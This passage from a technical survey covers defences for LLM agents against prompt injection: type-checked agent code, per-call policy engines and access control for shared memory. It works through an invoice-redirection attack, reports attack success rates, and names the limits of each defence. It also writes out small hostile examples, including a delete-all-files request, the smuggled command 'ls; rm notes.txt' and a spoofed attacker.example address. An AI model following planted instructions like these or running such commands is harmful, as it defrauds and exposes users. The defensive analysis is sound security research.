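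CaMeL's other failure was the quoted hotel review. The same attack caused the only failure of TACIT, a system that type-checks agents' programs, and was one of the attacks that FIDES's researchers discounted. In both the review and the payment attacks, the attacker's text does only what the user's request allows text from that source to do. Garby and colleagues conclude that four independent systems have reached a limit of information-flow control. A genuine bill and a forged one in the same file have the same source and label, so a system can tell them apart only by judging what they say or by using a record of the supplier's account from somewhere else.

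## Type-checking an agent's program before it runs

CaMeL and the LLMbda interpreter check an agent's program while it runs, so they may stop it halfway, for example after it has paid an invoice but before it has recorded the payment. A type checker examines the whole program first. If any line breaks a rule, the program doesn't run, and the model receives the error message and tries again. Several research groups now use the type checkers of existing languages for this, which lets an agent write the functions and recursion that CaMeL's small language leaves out.

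### Types that restrict effects

Most types describe the shape of data. A function of type `String -> Int` takes text and returns an integer, but in most languages it may also delete a file. Deleting a file is an effect, meaning an interaction with something outside the function. An effect type lists the effects a piece of code may have, so the compiler can reject code that has others.

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) gives the example of a public calculator. A visitor enters a calculation, a model writes a Haskell program to perform it, and the developer requires the program to have type `Int`. A malicious visitor asks for a program that deletes every file on the server and then computes the factorial of 5, and the model may write it. But in Haskell, any function that runs a system command has `IO` in its type, and so does a program that runs the command.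 The program therefore has type `IO Int` instead of `Int`, and the compiler rejects it.

Here, the type restricts both the final answer and what the program may do to produce it, whereas a schema that requires an integer restricts only the model's final answer.

Haskell code marked `IO` may use any file and any website, which is too broad for an agent that needs some effects and not others to do useful work. Developers can either define narrower marks, as Zhou and colleagues do, or use a language whose types name the particular files and connections a piece of code can reach.

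### TACIT and capture sets

Scala 3 can do the latter with an experimental feature called capture checking. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* describes TACIT, a server that Martin Odersky's group at EPFL in Lausanne built on this feature. The server compiles each snippet of Scala the agent sends and runs it if it passes. A capability here is a value that a program must hold to use a resource, much like Saltzer and Schroeder's unforgeable ticket. TACIT's designers assume that the model writing the snippets may be hostile, and they aim to keep private data from the model as well as from outsiders.

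The type of a value lists the capabilities it can reach, which form its capture set. Suppose that `out` is a file. A function that writes text to it has the type `String ->{out} Unit`, where `Unit` means that the function returns nothing of interest. A function with an empty capture set is pure, and its type is simply `String -> Unit`. The types form a chain:

`String -> Unit <: String ->{out} Unit <: String => Unit`

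The sign `<:` means that a value of the type on the left can be used where the type on the right is expected, and the double arrow allows any capabilities. A program can therefore pass a pure function anywhere, but it cannot pass a function that writes to `out` where the receiver requires a pure one.

TACIT uses this rule to protect private files. Their contents arrive in a wrapper, `Classified[String]`, which the agent cannot open. The agent can only pass the wrapper's `map` method a function to apply to the contents, and the result comes back wrapped. Since `map` accepts only pure functions, that function cannot print, save or send what it reads.

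Suppose that Ana asks what an invoice in her private folder is for. The agent could submit this:

```scala
val summary = requestFileSystem("/ana") { fs =>
  val bill = fs.access("/ana/private/invoice.txt").readClassified()
  chat(bill.map(text => s"What is this invoice for? $text"))
}
println(summary)
```

The first line opens Ana's folder and gives the block a capability for it, `fs`. The second line reads the invoice into a wrapper. The function inside `map` only joins two pieces of text, so it is pure. `chat` sends the result to a second model that Ana trusts with her data, perhaps one running on her own computer, and returns that model's answer in a wrapper. The compiler accepts the snippet.

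The last line writes to two channels. Ana sees the summary on a secure channel that only she can read, and the agent receives `Classified(****)` on the ordinary channel. If Ana then asks how long the summary is, the agent can submit `println(summary.map(_.length))`, and again only she sees the number. The planner in FIDES can inspect a hidden variable but gets a worse label as a result, whereas TACIT's agent never holds the plain text.

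Now suppose that the agent tries to copy the invoice into the notes Ana shares with Ben:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/ana") { fs =>
  val out = fs.access("/ana/shared/notes.txt")
  val bill = fs.access("/ana/private/invoice.txt").readClassified()
  bill.map(text => out.write(text))
}
```

The function in the fourth line uses `out`, so its type is `String ->{out} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The compiler reports the mismatch and nothing runs. In TACIT's own tests, the compiler rejected a snippet that would have written classified text to a file in this way, and others that called `println` inside `map`. An ordinary sandbox would have allowed the copy, because Ana's agent has permission to read the one file and to write the other.

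The compiler also prevents the agent from using a capability after its permission has ended. For example, the block can't return a function such as `() => fs.access("/ana/diary.txt").read()`, which the agent could call later. The function's capture set would contain `fs`, but `fs` exists only inside the block, so no type outside the block can include it. The compiler also rejects attempts to store `fs` in a list or an outside variable.

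The compiler cannot determine whether a file name that the program builds as it runs lies inside Ana's folder, so the library checks each path at run time. It also checks web addresses at run time, against a list of permitted hosts. TACIT compiles the agent's code in a restricted mode that forbids type casts and reflection, because these could prevent the compiler from tracking a capability. A program could also put a secret into an error message, so the library catches errors and can wrap them like any other private value.

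### ELBA and values that an agent cannot forge

In Zhou and colleagues' system, ELBA, the developer's own code and the agent's code are both in Haskell. The developer starts the agent by calling a function:

`agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t`

`Defs` lists the functions the agent may use, `Prompt` is the task, and `t` is the type the surrounding code expects. ELBA sends all three to a model, which writes a program. If the program has type `t`, ELBA runs it. Otherwise, ELBA returns the compiler's errors to the model for another attempt.

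Zhou and colleagues' main example is an agent that compiles bibliographies. Language models sometimes invent references, so the developer wants every entry to come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. In outline, the agent gets three functions:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
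```

The first returns the identifiers of matching papers, the second fetches an entry, and the third adds an entry to the file. The developer requires the agent's program to have type `BibIO ()`. Haskell's ordinary function for writing files is marked `IO`, so the program cannot call it, and the agent can write only through `appendToBibFile`.

That function accepts only a `Trusted Bib`. The constructor, the code that creates such a value, is hidden inside the developer's library, where only `dblpFetchBib` uses it. The agent can read an entry, sort entries by year or drop some, but it cannot turn its own text into a `Trusted Bib`. In 100 literature searches, none of ELBA's 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from an ordinary agent with a search tool.

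Any program may wrap a value in TACIT's `Classified`, but the agent cannot open the wrapper, which protects confidentiality. `Trusted` reverses these restrictions to protect integrity, so an agent may look inside a `Trusted` value but cannot make one.

Ana's invoice needs the second kind. Her developer could write a payment function that accepts only a `Trusted Account`, and make a lookup in Ana's supplier records the only source of such values. A program that passed the thief's account number to the payment function would not compile. The agent might still pick the wrong supplier, as it might with a fixed list.

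### Subagents and a general theorem

An ELBA program can call `agent`, so the system can react to what it finds. The bibliography agent might search, fetch the first result, and then start a subagent whose prompt includes that result. CaMeL's fixed plans rule this out, but ELBA allows it and relies on the type to limit the damage. Because the parent program has type `BibIO ()`, the subagent's program must have that type too, or a stricter one that the parent imposes, such as `Int`. The parent cannot give a subagent `IO` access that it lacks itself.

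Zhou and colleagues prove a general version of this. Write ⊢ e : t if the program e has type t, and let traces(e) be the set of sequences of tool calls with visible effects that e can produce. The type t guarantees a property P if, for every program e,

⊢ e : t implies P(traces(e)).

The theorem is that any property the types guarantee for ordinary programs also holds for programs that call agents. The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function that gets code from the model, type-checks it and runs it, or returns nothing if the check fails. This gives an ordinary program with the same type and traces, so the property holds for it. The model's code may contain further agent calls, so the proof uses induction on the depth of nesting, which has a fixed limit. The proof does not depend on the quality of the model's code.

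The theorem also means that a developer can use Haskell security libraries written long before agents existed. ELBA uses LIO, a library for information-flow control. An LIO program has a current label, which loses integrity when the program reads untrusted data, much like the context's label in FIDES. LIO stops the program if it then tries to write somewhere that requires higher integrity, so a program can lose the ability to write to places it could write to before, as under Biba's policy.

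LIO's function `toLabeled` limits that danger. It runs a subagent separately, lets the subagent's label drop, and returns the answer in a labelled wrapper without changing the parent's label. The parent can pass the wrapper to a tool without opening it. Unlike the quarantined model in the dual-LLM pattern, the subagent may call any tool its current label allows.

LIO checks these labels at run time. The type checker guarantees only that the agent's code cannot bypass LIO, so a program that compiles may still stop halfway.

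### ELBA and CaMeL on the same tasks

Zhou and colleagues ran both systems on AgentDojo's Slack suite. They also ran each of the suite's 105 attack cases with three styles of injected text, for 315 attacked runs per model. The table shows how many tasks each system completed with its policies on.

| Model | ELBA, no attack (of 21) | CaMeL, no attack (of 21) | ELBA, attacked (of 315) | CaMeL, attacked (of 315) |
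|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 10 | 5 | 153 | 69 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 9 | 6 | 141 | 89 |
| GPT-5.4 | 10 | 5 | 148 | 74 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 8 | 4 | 129 | 71 |

ELBA completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL, both with and without attacks. Its lead is clearest in the attacked runs. With only 21 tasks, the 95% confidence interval for Opus 4.8 without attacks ranges from a 7-percentage-point lead for CaMeL to a 34-point lead for ELBA.

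Part of the difference may come from the policies. CaMeL used its own, while ELBA used a new one, under which a model that reads untrusted data drops to the privileges of whoever supplied it. With policies off and no attack, the two systems did almost equally well, completing 64 and 61 of 84 tasks. Zhou and colleagues suggest testing different systems under the same policies, which would show how much of ELBA's lead comes from its design. ELBA also took about three times as long, because it calls a model again as data comes in.

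The comparison doesn't show which of the two is more secure, because no attack succeeded against either, even with policies off. When the researchers forced ELBA's subagents to follow the attacker's instructions, its policies blocked every attack.

TACIT's results against CaMeL are mixed. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the two completed similar shares of AgentDojo's tasks in three suites, but in Travel TACIT completed 64.3% and CaMeL 1.4%. With o4-mini, TACIT completed 52.9% in Workspace and 47.6% in Slack, well below the 81.4% and 68.6% that CaMeL's designers reported.

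### How often programs fail the check

Models have seen little Scala with capture checking, but in tests by TACIT's designers they usually wrote it without needing another attempt. The tests used three models on airline and retail tasks from τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service. DeepSeek V3.2 had the highest retry rate, with 7.93% of its snippets on airline tasks needing another attempt. The rates for the other five combinations of model and task type were all below 1.6%, and the lowest was 0.32%. Snippets that failed needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average, and compiling usually took less than a second.

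Many of the errors were simple mistakes. Models did not handle a value that might be missing, or wrote `$50` in text where Scala reads a dollar sign as the start of a variable name. In ELBA, runs on AgentDojo averaged 0.13 retries, and 7 of 2,688 used up all their attempts without producing a valid program.

The rate was higher in *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the EPFL group. It brings TACIT closer to ELBA's design with an `agent[T](task)` call that a program can make at any point. The model's code may use whatever variables and tools exist at that point, so they serve as its list of permissions. On BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of the model's programs, with an average of 0.7 retries per question.

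Retrying a rejected program is harmless because no part of it has run. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the agent has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as an integer. The first line of the model's program subtracts the money, but the second returns a sentence. The compiler rejects the whole program, so the balance stays at 100. A Python program with a similar mistake could subtract the money, fail on the next line, and subtract it again on the second attempt.

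### ETAS and the order of actions

Ana might want a rule that her assistant must ask her before it pays anyone. A list of permitted effects cannot express this, because it doesn't record their order. Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, present a language that can. Their example is an agent that edits software. Write g for a request for approval and w for a request to write a file. The rule is

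`Approval.request >> Repo.apply`

which allows the sequences

P = 1 ⊔ g; (g ⊔ w)*.

Here, 1 is the empty sequence, ⊔ means "or", the semicolon means "followed by", and the star means any number of repetitions. A program may therefore do nothing, or ask first and then ask or write as often as it likes. The compiler also works out which sequences a program can produce. One that asks for approval and writes only if the answer is yes has

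A = g; (1 ⊔ w),

and every sequence in A, complete or cut short, is also in P. The compiler accepts the program without further checks. It rejects a program that always writes first. If some paths obey the rule and others break it, the compiler adds a monitor that checks each request at run time.

Developers often test an agent with a substitute for the write operation that changes nothing. Languages with effect types normally drop an effect from a function's type once a substitute handles it, so an attempt to write without approval could go unnoticed in a test. ETAS avoids this by keeping a separate record of every request, whether or not the request changes anything.

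The rule only requires the program to request approval, so one request satisfies it for any number of writes, whatever Ana answers. The program also has to check her answer, and the software that performs the write has to check that the approval covers that particular change. Tan and colleagues' evidence is also limited so far. Their compiler accepted two correct test programs and rejected four faulty ones, and a coding agent's controller behaved as expected in ten scripted scenarios.

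### Turn and opaque credentials

*Turn* (Kizito, 2026) describes a language that checks less in advance but builds typed model answers into its syntax. A programmer writes `infer Invoice { prompt }`, where `Invoice` is a record type. The compiler turns the type into a JSON Schema, and the program checks the model's answer against that schema before using it. If the answer doesn't fit, the program queries the model again, up to three times by default, and then raises an error.

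Turn also lets a program get the `confidence` of an answer and choose a branch accordingly. This is a number from 0 to 1, usually computed from the probabilities the model gave to its tokens. If the service doesn't provide those probabilities, the value is 0.5. A program that uses a default when confidence is below 0.7, as in Kizito's example, would then use the default every time. Confidence also doesn't measure safety, since a model can assign high probability to a false account number.

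The other addition is a type for credentials. A program that needs to log in to Ana's bank receives an `Identity` value, which it cannot print, convert to text or save. The runtime, the software that executes the program, adds the real password to the outgoing request. An injected instruction to reveal the password would fail because the program never holds it. The program could still use the `Identity` value to misuse the account, so Ana would also need a payment rule.

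Ordinary variables in Turn have no fixed types, which Kizito acknowledges as a limitation, so many type errors appear only when the program runs.

### What a well-typed program can still do

A pure function cannot send a secret, but its running time can depend on the secret. A hostile agent could have `map` do a long calculation only if the invoice contains the word "overdue", and learn one bit from how long the reply takes. A function that never finishes would reveal a bit in the same way. TACIT's guarantee excludes such channels, and ELBA's traces of tool calls don't record time. An agent that can submit many snippets can learn more bits by repeating this, as with the retries in CaMeL.

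External commands are a larger gap, because the compiler cannot check what another program does once a TACIT program starts it. The only protection left is the list of permitted commands. TACIT's designers recommend keeping that list short and specific, with entries such as `git diff`, and running the commands in a sandbox. The gap matters most for coding agents, which frequently run compilers and tests.

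All these guarantees also depend on a library being written correctly. TACIT's library is about 1,000 lines long, and each new set of tools needs a few hundred more. Some of this code has to break the rules that the agent's code must follow. For example, a cache stores results in a variable, which counts as an effect even though it can't be observed from outside. A programmer marks such code `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler treats it as safe without checking. The compiler also cannot verify that the model behind `chat` retains nothing from one invoice when it processes the next.

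TACIT's AgentDojo tests show how much depends on how a tool's author writes its type. Bills arrive in a `Classified` wrapper, but the payment tool's type requires no capability, and according to the model's instructions, effects inside `map` happen immediately. A program can therefore apparently extract an account number from a bill and pay that account inside `map`. The agent needs this freedom to pay genuine bills, but it would also let a thief who has changed the number on a bill receive the payment.

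Finally, a program can pass every check and still give the wrong answer. For example, ELBA's bibliography may consist of real papers on the wrong subject. The line planted in Ana's invoice may also influence the trusted model that summarises the invoice, so that she reads on her secure channel that the supplier has changed banks.

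## Access rules checked at each tool call

CaMeL, TACIT and ELBA need an agent that writes its actions as programs. Most agents instead call one tool after another. A developer can protect these agents without rebuilding them by placing a rule engine between the agent and its tools. The engine is a reference monitor that checks each proposed call against a set of rules, then forwards or refuses it.

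*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes an engine that can run as a proxy. A user redirects an existing agent's model and tool connections to the proxy without changing the agent's code. The proxy cannot check tools built into the agent that never use those connections.

### One payment, one decision

A rule can draw on five kinds of information, shown here for Ana's invoice.

| Input | Value |
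|---|---|
| User | Ana |
| Agent | her assistant |
| Tool | `send_payment` |
| Arguments | the account number and 40,000 cents |
| History | the assistant has read an outside e-mail, and Ana has approved nothing |

If the rules allow the call, the engine sends it to the bank. If not, Progent can stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message in place of the tool's result. By default, the message includes the reason and an instruction to try other tools or arguments, so the agent can still finish the rest of its task. A hijacked agent can use the same message to work out which calls the rules allow.

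Amazon's cloud business, AWS, sells an engine of this kind. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), customers have been able to use it since 3 March in thirteen regions. A gateway intercepts the agent's calls and checks them against rules in Cedar, AWS's open-source policy language. The gateway AWS describes blocks everything that no rule permits. A rule for Ana, modelled on the refund example in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* and with the gateway's address shortened, could be:

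```
permit(
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Bank__send_payment",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"ana-gateway"
) when {
  principal.hasTag("username") &&
  principal.getTag("username") == "ana" &&
  context.input.amount_cents <= 50000 &&
  ["10023456", "10078901"].contains(context.input.account)
};
```

The first part of the rule names the kind of user, the tool and the gateway. The conditions require that the user is Ana, that the payment is at most €500, and that the account belongs to one of the two suppliers she has on file. The thief's account belongs to neither, so the gateway refuses the payment. It would also refuse a payment to a genuine new supplier until somebody changed the rule.

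Small mistakes in writing such a rule can change what it allows. AWS describes the limit in its refund example as "$500 or less", but the Cedar condition is `amount < 500`, which blocks a refund of exactly $500. AWS also offers a tool that converts plain English to Cedar, and tells developers to check that the result matches what they meant.

Ana's rule checks the user, the tool and the arguments, but not the agent or the history. According to AWS, a permission rule can read the call's input but no other field of the context. The assistant could pay the same €400 invoice ten times, because each payment satisfies the rule.

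### Rules that match text

A shell command is much harder to check against a list than an account number, because one string can contain several actions. A rule that allows any command starting with `ls`, which lists files, also allows `ls; rm notes.txt`, which then deletes one. Matching the program's name doesn't solve this, since `find` normally searches for files but deletes them if the command includes `-delete`. In the `ping` leak from Claude Code, too, the permitted program could do more than the person who permitted it had considered.

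*Authority Is Not a String* (2026) presents CapScope, which grants a coding agent authority to read, write or execute within a defined scope. A model predicts what the task will need before anything reads the project's files or any tool output. Ordinary code validates the prediction and turns it into an upper limit on the agent's authority for the whole task. Text planted in the project cannot influence that limit, although the prediction may still be too broad.

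### Rules written for one task

Ana's fixed rule works for payments to known suppliers. Nobody can write rules in advance for everything she might request, so Progent has a language model write the rules for each task.

A Progent policy is a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids a tool under conditions on its arguments, and includes a fallback for refused calls. To check a call, the program selects the rules for that tool and tries the `forbid` rules first. The first rule whose conditions hold decides the outcome. If none holds, the program refuses the call.

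Before the agent starts, the policy model reads the user's request and the tool descriptions and writes the first policy. It may propose changes as tool results come in. Suppose Ana types, "Do the things Ben asked for in his last e-mail," a request that CaMeL cannot plan safely. Progent's first policy might allow only the search for that e-mail. If Ben asked for a summary to be posted on Slack, the policy model then proposes adding the Slack tool.

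The new proposal may be a response to planted text, so ordinary code compares it with the old policy. Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

and otherwise it is an expansion. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a logical formula, looks for a call that P′ allows and P refuses. Replacing two permitted accounts with one different account counts as an expansion, even though the list gets shorter. Progent applies narrowings automatically and sends expansions for approval, which may come from a person or a preset rule. Shi and colleagues call the result monotonic confinement: the set of permitted calls cannot grow without approval.

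With GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy model, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. On ASB, a benchmark with ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agent remained about as useful in both tests. Shi and colleagues left out two AgentDojo attacks that only steer the agent towards another hotel, because Progent isn't designed to stop them.

Those headline results provide little evidence about monotonic confinement, because the researchers automatically approved every expansion to imitate a careless user. They mainly show that GPT-4o usually wrote suitable rules. The first policy, with no updates, cut AgentDojo's rate to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, the rate fell to zero, but the researchers assumed the reviewer would never allow payments to any recipient whatsoever without restriction. Only 6% of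 updates were expansions, so the reviewer would have had few to read.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile tool results could cause Progent to loosen its rules when it updates them. In Progent's own tests, attacks written to do this raised the attack success rate only slightly, and an independent adaptive test by Narisetty and colleagues did not defeat the defence either.

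Ana's invoice could get past the solver without any loosening. Her request doesn't name an account, so the first policy may allow a payment to anyone. After the assistant reads the e-mail, the policy model may restrict payments to the account number in it. That is a narrowing, so Progent applies it without approval, and the policy now allows a payment to the thief and to nobody else. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within the permissions a task needs. Ana can close this gap with a fixed rule, which Progent checks before the task's own rules. In Progent's notation, it might be:

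```
forbid send_payment
when { not (account in ["10023456", "10078901"]) },
fallback return "This account is not on file."
```

Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, describe a stricter way to use a policy model. Their system, Conseca, writes one policy from the user's request and information the developer trusts, and never shows the policy model the contents of e-mails or files. In their example, where the user wants the agent to answer urgent work e-mails, the policy lets the agent send messages with "urgent" in the subject from the user's address to work addresses, and forbids it to delete anything. Each rule comes with a reason in plain English, which the program returns to the agent when it refuses a call.

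The researchers tested Conseca on 20 office tasks, five times each.

| Policy | Tasks completed, average of 20 | Blocked an inappropriate request to forward e-mails |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | no |
| Fixed: everything except deletion | 12.2 | no |
| Fixed: no changes of any kind | 0.0 | yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 | yes |

The security test used a single planted message, so the last column shows only that the idea can work. Like CaMeL's planner, Conseca cannot predict actions that depend on what an e-mail contains. The example policy's pattern also matches `@work.com` anywhere in the recipient's address, so it would wrongly accept `ben@work.com.attacker.example`.

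Google's coding agent Gemini CLI includes a Conseca option, which is off by default according to a copy of the agent's settings guide hosted by Mintlify.

Other evidence suggests that models are unreliable at choosing permissions. *Trust Is Not a Score* (2026) cites a study in which frontier models left out permissions that a task needed and granted sensitive ones that it didn't need. Making the model more cautious would fix only the second error. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes formally verifying generated policies, but a verifier needs a precise statement to check the policy against, and Ana's sentence is too imprecise for that.

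### Permitted calls that together leak data

If Ana's assistant is allowed to read her calendar and send e-mail, a rule engine that checks each call separately will let it e-mail her calendar to a stranger. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) describes a similar leak. A user tired of approval prompts gives an agent standing permission to search a sales folder, but the permission covers every use of the search tool, including searches of the home directory. The agent can then send out private files with an e-mail tool that the user has also approved.

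A rule needs the history to catch this. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, which records messages, tool calls and results as points in a graph and links each one to the earlier events that may have influenced it. Since a model reads its whole context, FORGE links the model's output to every message in that context.

Developers write FORGE's rules in Datalog, a language for querying databases. The sign `:-` means "if", and a comma means "and":

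```
Tainted(e) :- UntrustedInput(e).
Tainted(e) :- DependsOn(e, e'), Tainted(e').
Deny(a)    :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

The first two rules mark an event as tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on a tainted event. Two similar rules define `HasSecret`. If the assistant reads the invoice e-mail and Ana's calendar, then tries to send a message to an outsider, the message depends on both, so FORGE refuses to send it. Evaluating Datalog rules on a finite set of facts always ends with a single answer. In one set of tests, the median check took less than a millisecond.

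Rules that use history can also require an earlier event, such as an approval. Palumbo and colleagues applied FORGE to a group of agents that look up drug information and need a supervisor's approval before they query a US government database. Without FORGE, the agents made 40 unauthorised queries in 15 runs. With it, they made none. All 15 answers were correct both with and without FORGE.

Refusals can improve an agent's work. In simulated airline customer service, the average success rate rose from 74.7% to 81.5% when FORGE checked requests against the company's rules. An agent that tried to make a forbidden booking was told why it was refused and could correct itself. GPT-5.2 improved from 63.0% to 77.5%, but Gemini 3.1 Pro fell from 82.5% to 81.0%.

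The researchers compared two policies on AgentDojo using GPT-4o. FIDES's policy blocks consequential calls once the context contains untrusted text. The provenance policy checks whether the user requested the action and whether its target came from an acceptable source, so it can allow a call even after the agent has read untrusted text. All four agents in the table received the user's request again after each batch of tool results.

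| Rules | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, attacked | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| A model chooses the permitted tools in advance | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
| FORGE with FIDES's policy | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.3% |
| FORGE with the provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.2% |

The comparison puts FIDES at a disadvantage, because FORGE applied the FIDES policy to an ordinary agent without the variables that FIDES uses to keep the context trusted. The provenance policy still lowered the task completion rate by about 21 percentage points compared with no rules. The last column leaves out attacks whose calls FORGE blocked. The remaining attacks succeeded through the text of the agent's answers, which FORGE did not check. FORGE also cannot check actions outside the channels it monitors, such as a program opening its own network connection.

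*Before the Tool Call* (2026) describes PCAS, another reference monitor with Datalog-style rules. PCAS raised policy compliance from 48% to 93% with no violations in the monitored runs, so the 93% must measure something besides violations, perhaps whether the agent also finished the task. PCAS is probably an earlier version of FORGE, because the designs match closely and Palumbo and colleagues describe FORGE as the first use of Datalog for this purpose. They would be unlikely to claim this if another group had built PCAS.

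### Whose rights the agent uses

Suppose Ana's company gives the assistant its own account, which can open every employee's files. Ben asks it for Ana's salary letter, and the file server sends the letter because the assistant has permission to read it. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy because it uses its own authority on behalf of someone who lacks it.

Passing on Ben's identity would prevent this, since the file server could then apply Ben's rights. AWS lists the failure to do so among common mistakes, because every call then runs with the agent's permissions. The agent needs limits of its own too. Microsoft (2026) warns that an agent without a managed identity and narrowly defined roles may reach data its owner never intended it to use. A careful system therefore gives each call only the rights in

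R_user ∩ R_agent ∩ R_task,

meaning those that the user holds, the agent may exercise and the task requires.

The identity in a rule can be ambiguous because it may refer to a person or an agent. One of AWS's refund examples permits calls from "John", and another permits calls from "refund-agent". If the gateway receives only the agent's name, the second rule gives everyone who can talk to the agent the same access.

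Prompt injection also creates a confused deputy, and passing on the user's identity doesn't help there. A thief who injects instructions into Ana's assistant has no right to use her bank account, but Ana does, and the assistant is working for her, so only a rule about the payment itself can stop the theft. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) audited common agent frameworks and found that they control which tools an agent has but, by default, do not authorise each call, so an assistant with a payment tool may pay anyone.

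Agents usually receive a user's rights through OAuth, a protocol that lets an application use someone's account without the password. The application gets a token with scopes, such as permission to read mail but not send it. The Model Context Protocol follows this approach. According to *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026), the protocol's 2026 rules recommend starting with minimal scopes and requesting more when the agent needs them. A server checking a token must also account for the fact that a broad scope can include narrower ones.

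### Finding the fewest permissions

Agents that choose their own tools often pick ones with more privileges than the task needs. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a test with 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents picked an over-privileged tool more than 30% of the time.

*MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) calculates the permissions instead. It groups tools by OAuth scope and ranks a scope as broader if it covers more tools. When the agent submits a plan, an optimisation program finds the narrowest set of scopes that covers it. The user approves any new scopes, much like app permissions on a phone, and *MiniScope* then checks every tool call. The agent never holds the user's credentials.

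Zhu and colleagues tested MiniScope with synthetic requests for ten real applications, including Gmail and Slack. It added 1% to 6% to the running time. When a language model chose the permissions instead, commercial models scored 70% to 83% for minimality and open models scored 20% to 34%. The solver also found six existing connectors that had more permissions than they needed. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, users had to confirm between 18% and 60% of the time, depending on their habits.

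MiniScope calculates the minimum permissions from the agent's plan, which may already be corrupt. If a planted line adds a step that sends mail, the minimum will include permission to send mail, and Ana can stop it only by refusing permission. Once she grants that scope, MiniScope does not limit whom the agent writes to. There may also be more than one minimum. For example, a task that needs only mail might be able to use either a scope that covers mail and contacts or one that covers mail and calendar. Neither scope includes the other, so choosing between them requires a judgement about which data matters more.

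Permissions can also grow when an agent delegates work. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) therefore applies least privilege to delegation as well as to tools, arguments and returned data. In CapScope, the main agent requests permissions for each subagent along with the subtask, and these must fall within the limit that the code set at the start. An assistant that asks a subagent to read Ana's invoice could give the subagent access to that one file but no payment tool.

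## Who may read a memory shared by several users and agents

A memory lookup is a tool call, so a rule engine can decide whether Ana's assistant may search the memory she shares with Ben. The memory also needs rules for individual entries to determine which ones the search may return, because some notes concern only Ana, some are for her and Ben, and others come from Ben's work with another colleague, Cara.

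Most systems lack access controls for shared memory. According to the March 2026 survey *Memory for Autonomous LLM Agents*, multi-agent frameworks either share all memory, which leaks private information, or give each agent a separate store, which stops agents from using one another's knowledge. The survey describes database-style access lists as a natural but unexplored solution, although Rezazadeh, Li and colleagues (2025) had published a closely related design, *Collaborative Memory*, ten months earlier.

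### An entry as a typed record

If an entry is only a piece of text, code cannot tell who may read it. A typed record adds fields that code can check. Ana's note about a supplier might look like this:

| Field | Value | What code can do with it |
|---|---|---|
| Content | "The paper supplier's account is 10023456" | search it |
| Owner | Ana | let only Ana change the permissions |
| Readers | Ana, Ben | withhold the entry from everyone else |
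| Purpose | paying invoices | withhold it from other tasks |
| Time | valid until 31 December | stop returning it after that date |
| Version | 2, replaces 1 | return only the latest version |
| Derived from | nothing; Ana typed it | find the summaries that depend on an entry |

MemOS treats memory as a resource for an operating system to manage, and packages memories with their metadata in units called MemCubes (described in *AIM*, Johnson, Kumankumah and colleagues, 2026). Records in *MemTX* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) have an owner, a validity period, links to their sources, and separate lists of roles that may read and write. Separate lists are useful because many people who need to read a note have no reason to change it. In *Shared Selective Persistent Memory for Agentic LLM Systems* (2026), for example, viewers can load and query a shared workspace, but only its owners and stewards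 can edit it.

### Where the checks belong

Lin, Hao and colleagues (2026), in *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents*, divide the life of a memory into six phases: writing, storing, retrieving, acting on it, sharing, and forgetting. Permission comes up repeatedly across these phases.

When the assistant writes Ana's note, code should set the owner and readers from the logged-in session. If the model chose them, a line in an e-mail could cause it to make the note public. (Whether the note's content can be trusted is a separate question.) When someone searches, code checks whether that person is on a note's list of readers before any of its text enters the model's context. When a model summarises several notes, code determines who may read the summary. Someone with the authority to share a note must explicitly approve any wider access, and deleting a note requires finding its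 copies and summaries.

Every way of reading the memory has to include the permission check. *Cross-agent memory sharing*, developer documentation from the database company Neo4j, warns that a field stored with a memory does not automatically filter every read. One of Neo4j's search functions accepts a session identifier but doesn't use it to restrict the results, so passing the identifier would not separate Ana's conversations from Ben's.

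### Filtering before the model reads

A developer could instead use black-box treatment, which puts every relevant entry in the context and instructs the model to reveal only what the current user may know. Ben might still get a secret out with an indirect question, or a planted instruction might make the model copy it into an e-mail. Checking the final answer doesn't fix this, because the model has already read the secret. Liu (2026) points out in *Audience-Bound Persistent Memory* that a model can give an acceptable answer even when its context contains a forbidden fact, so a test that examines only answers will miss the exposure.

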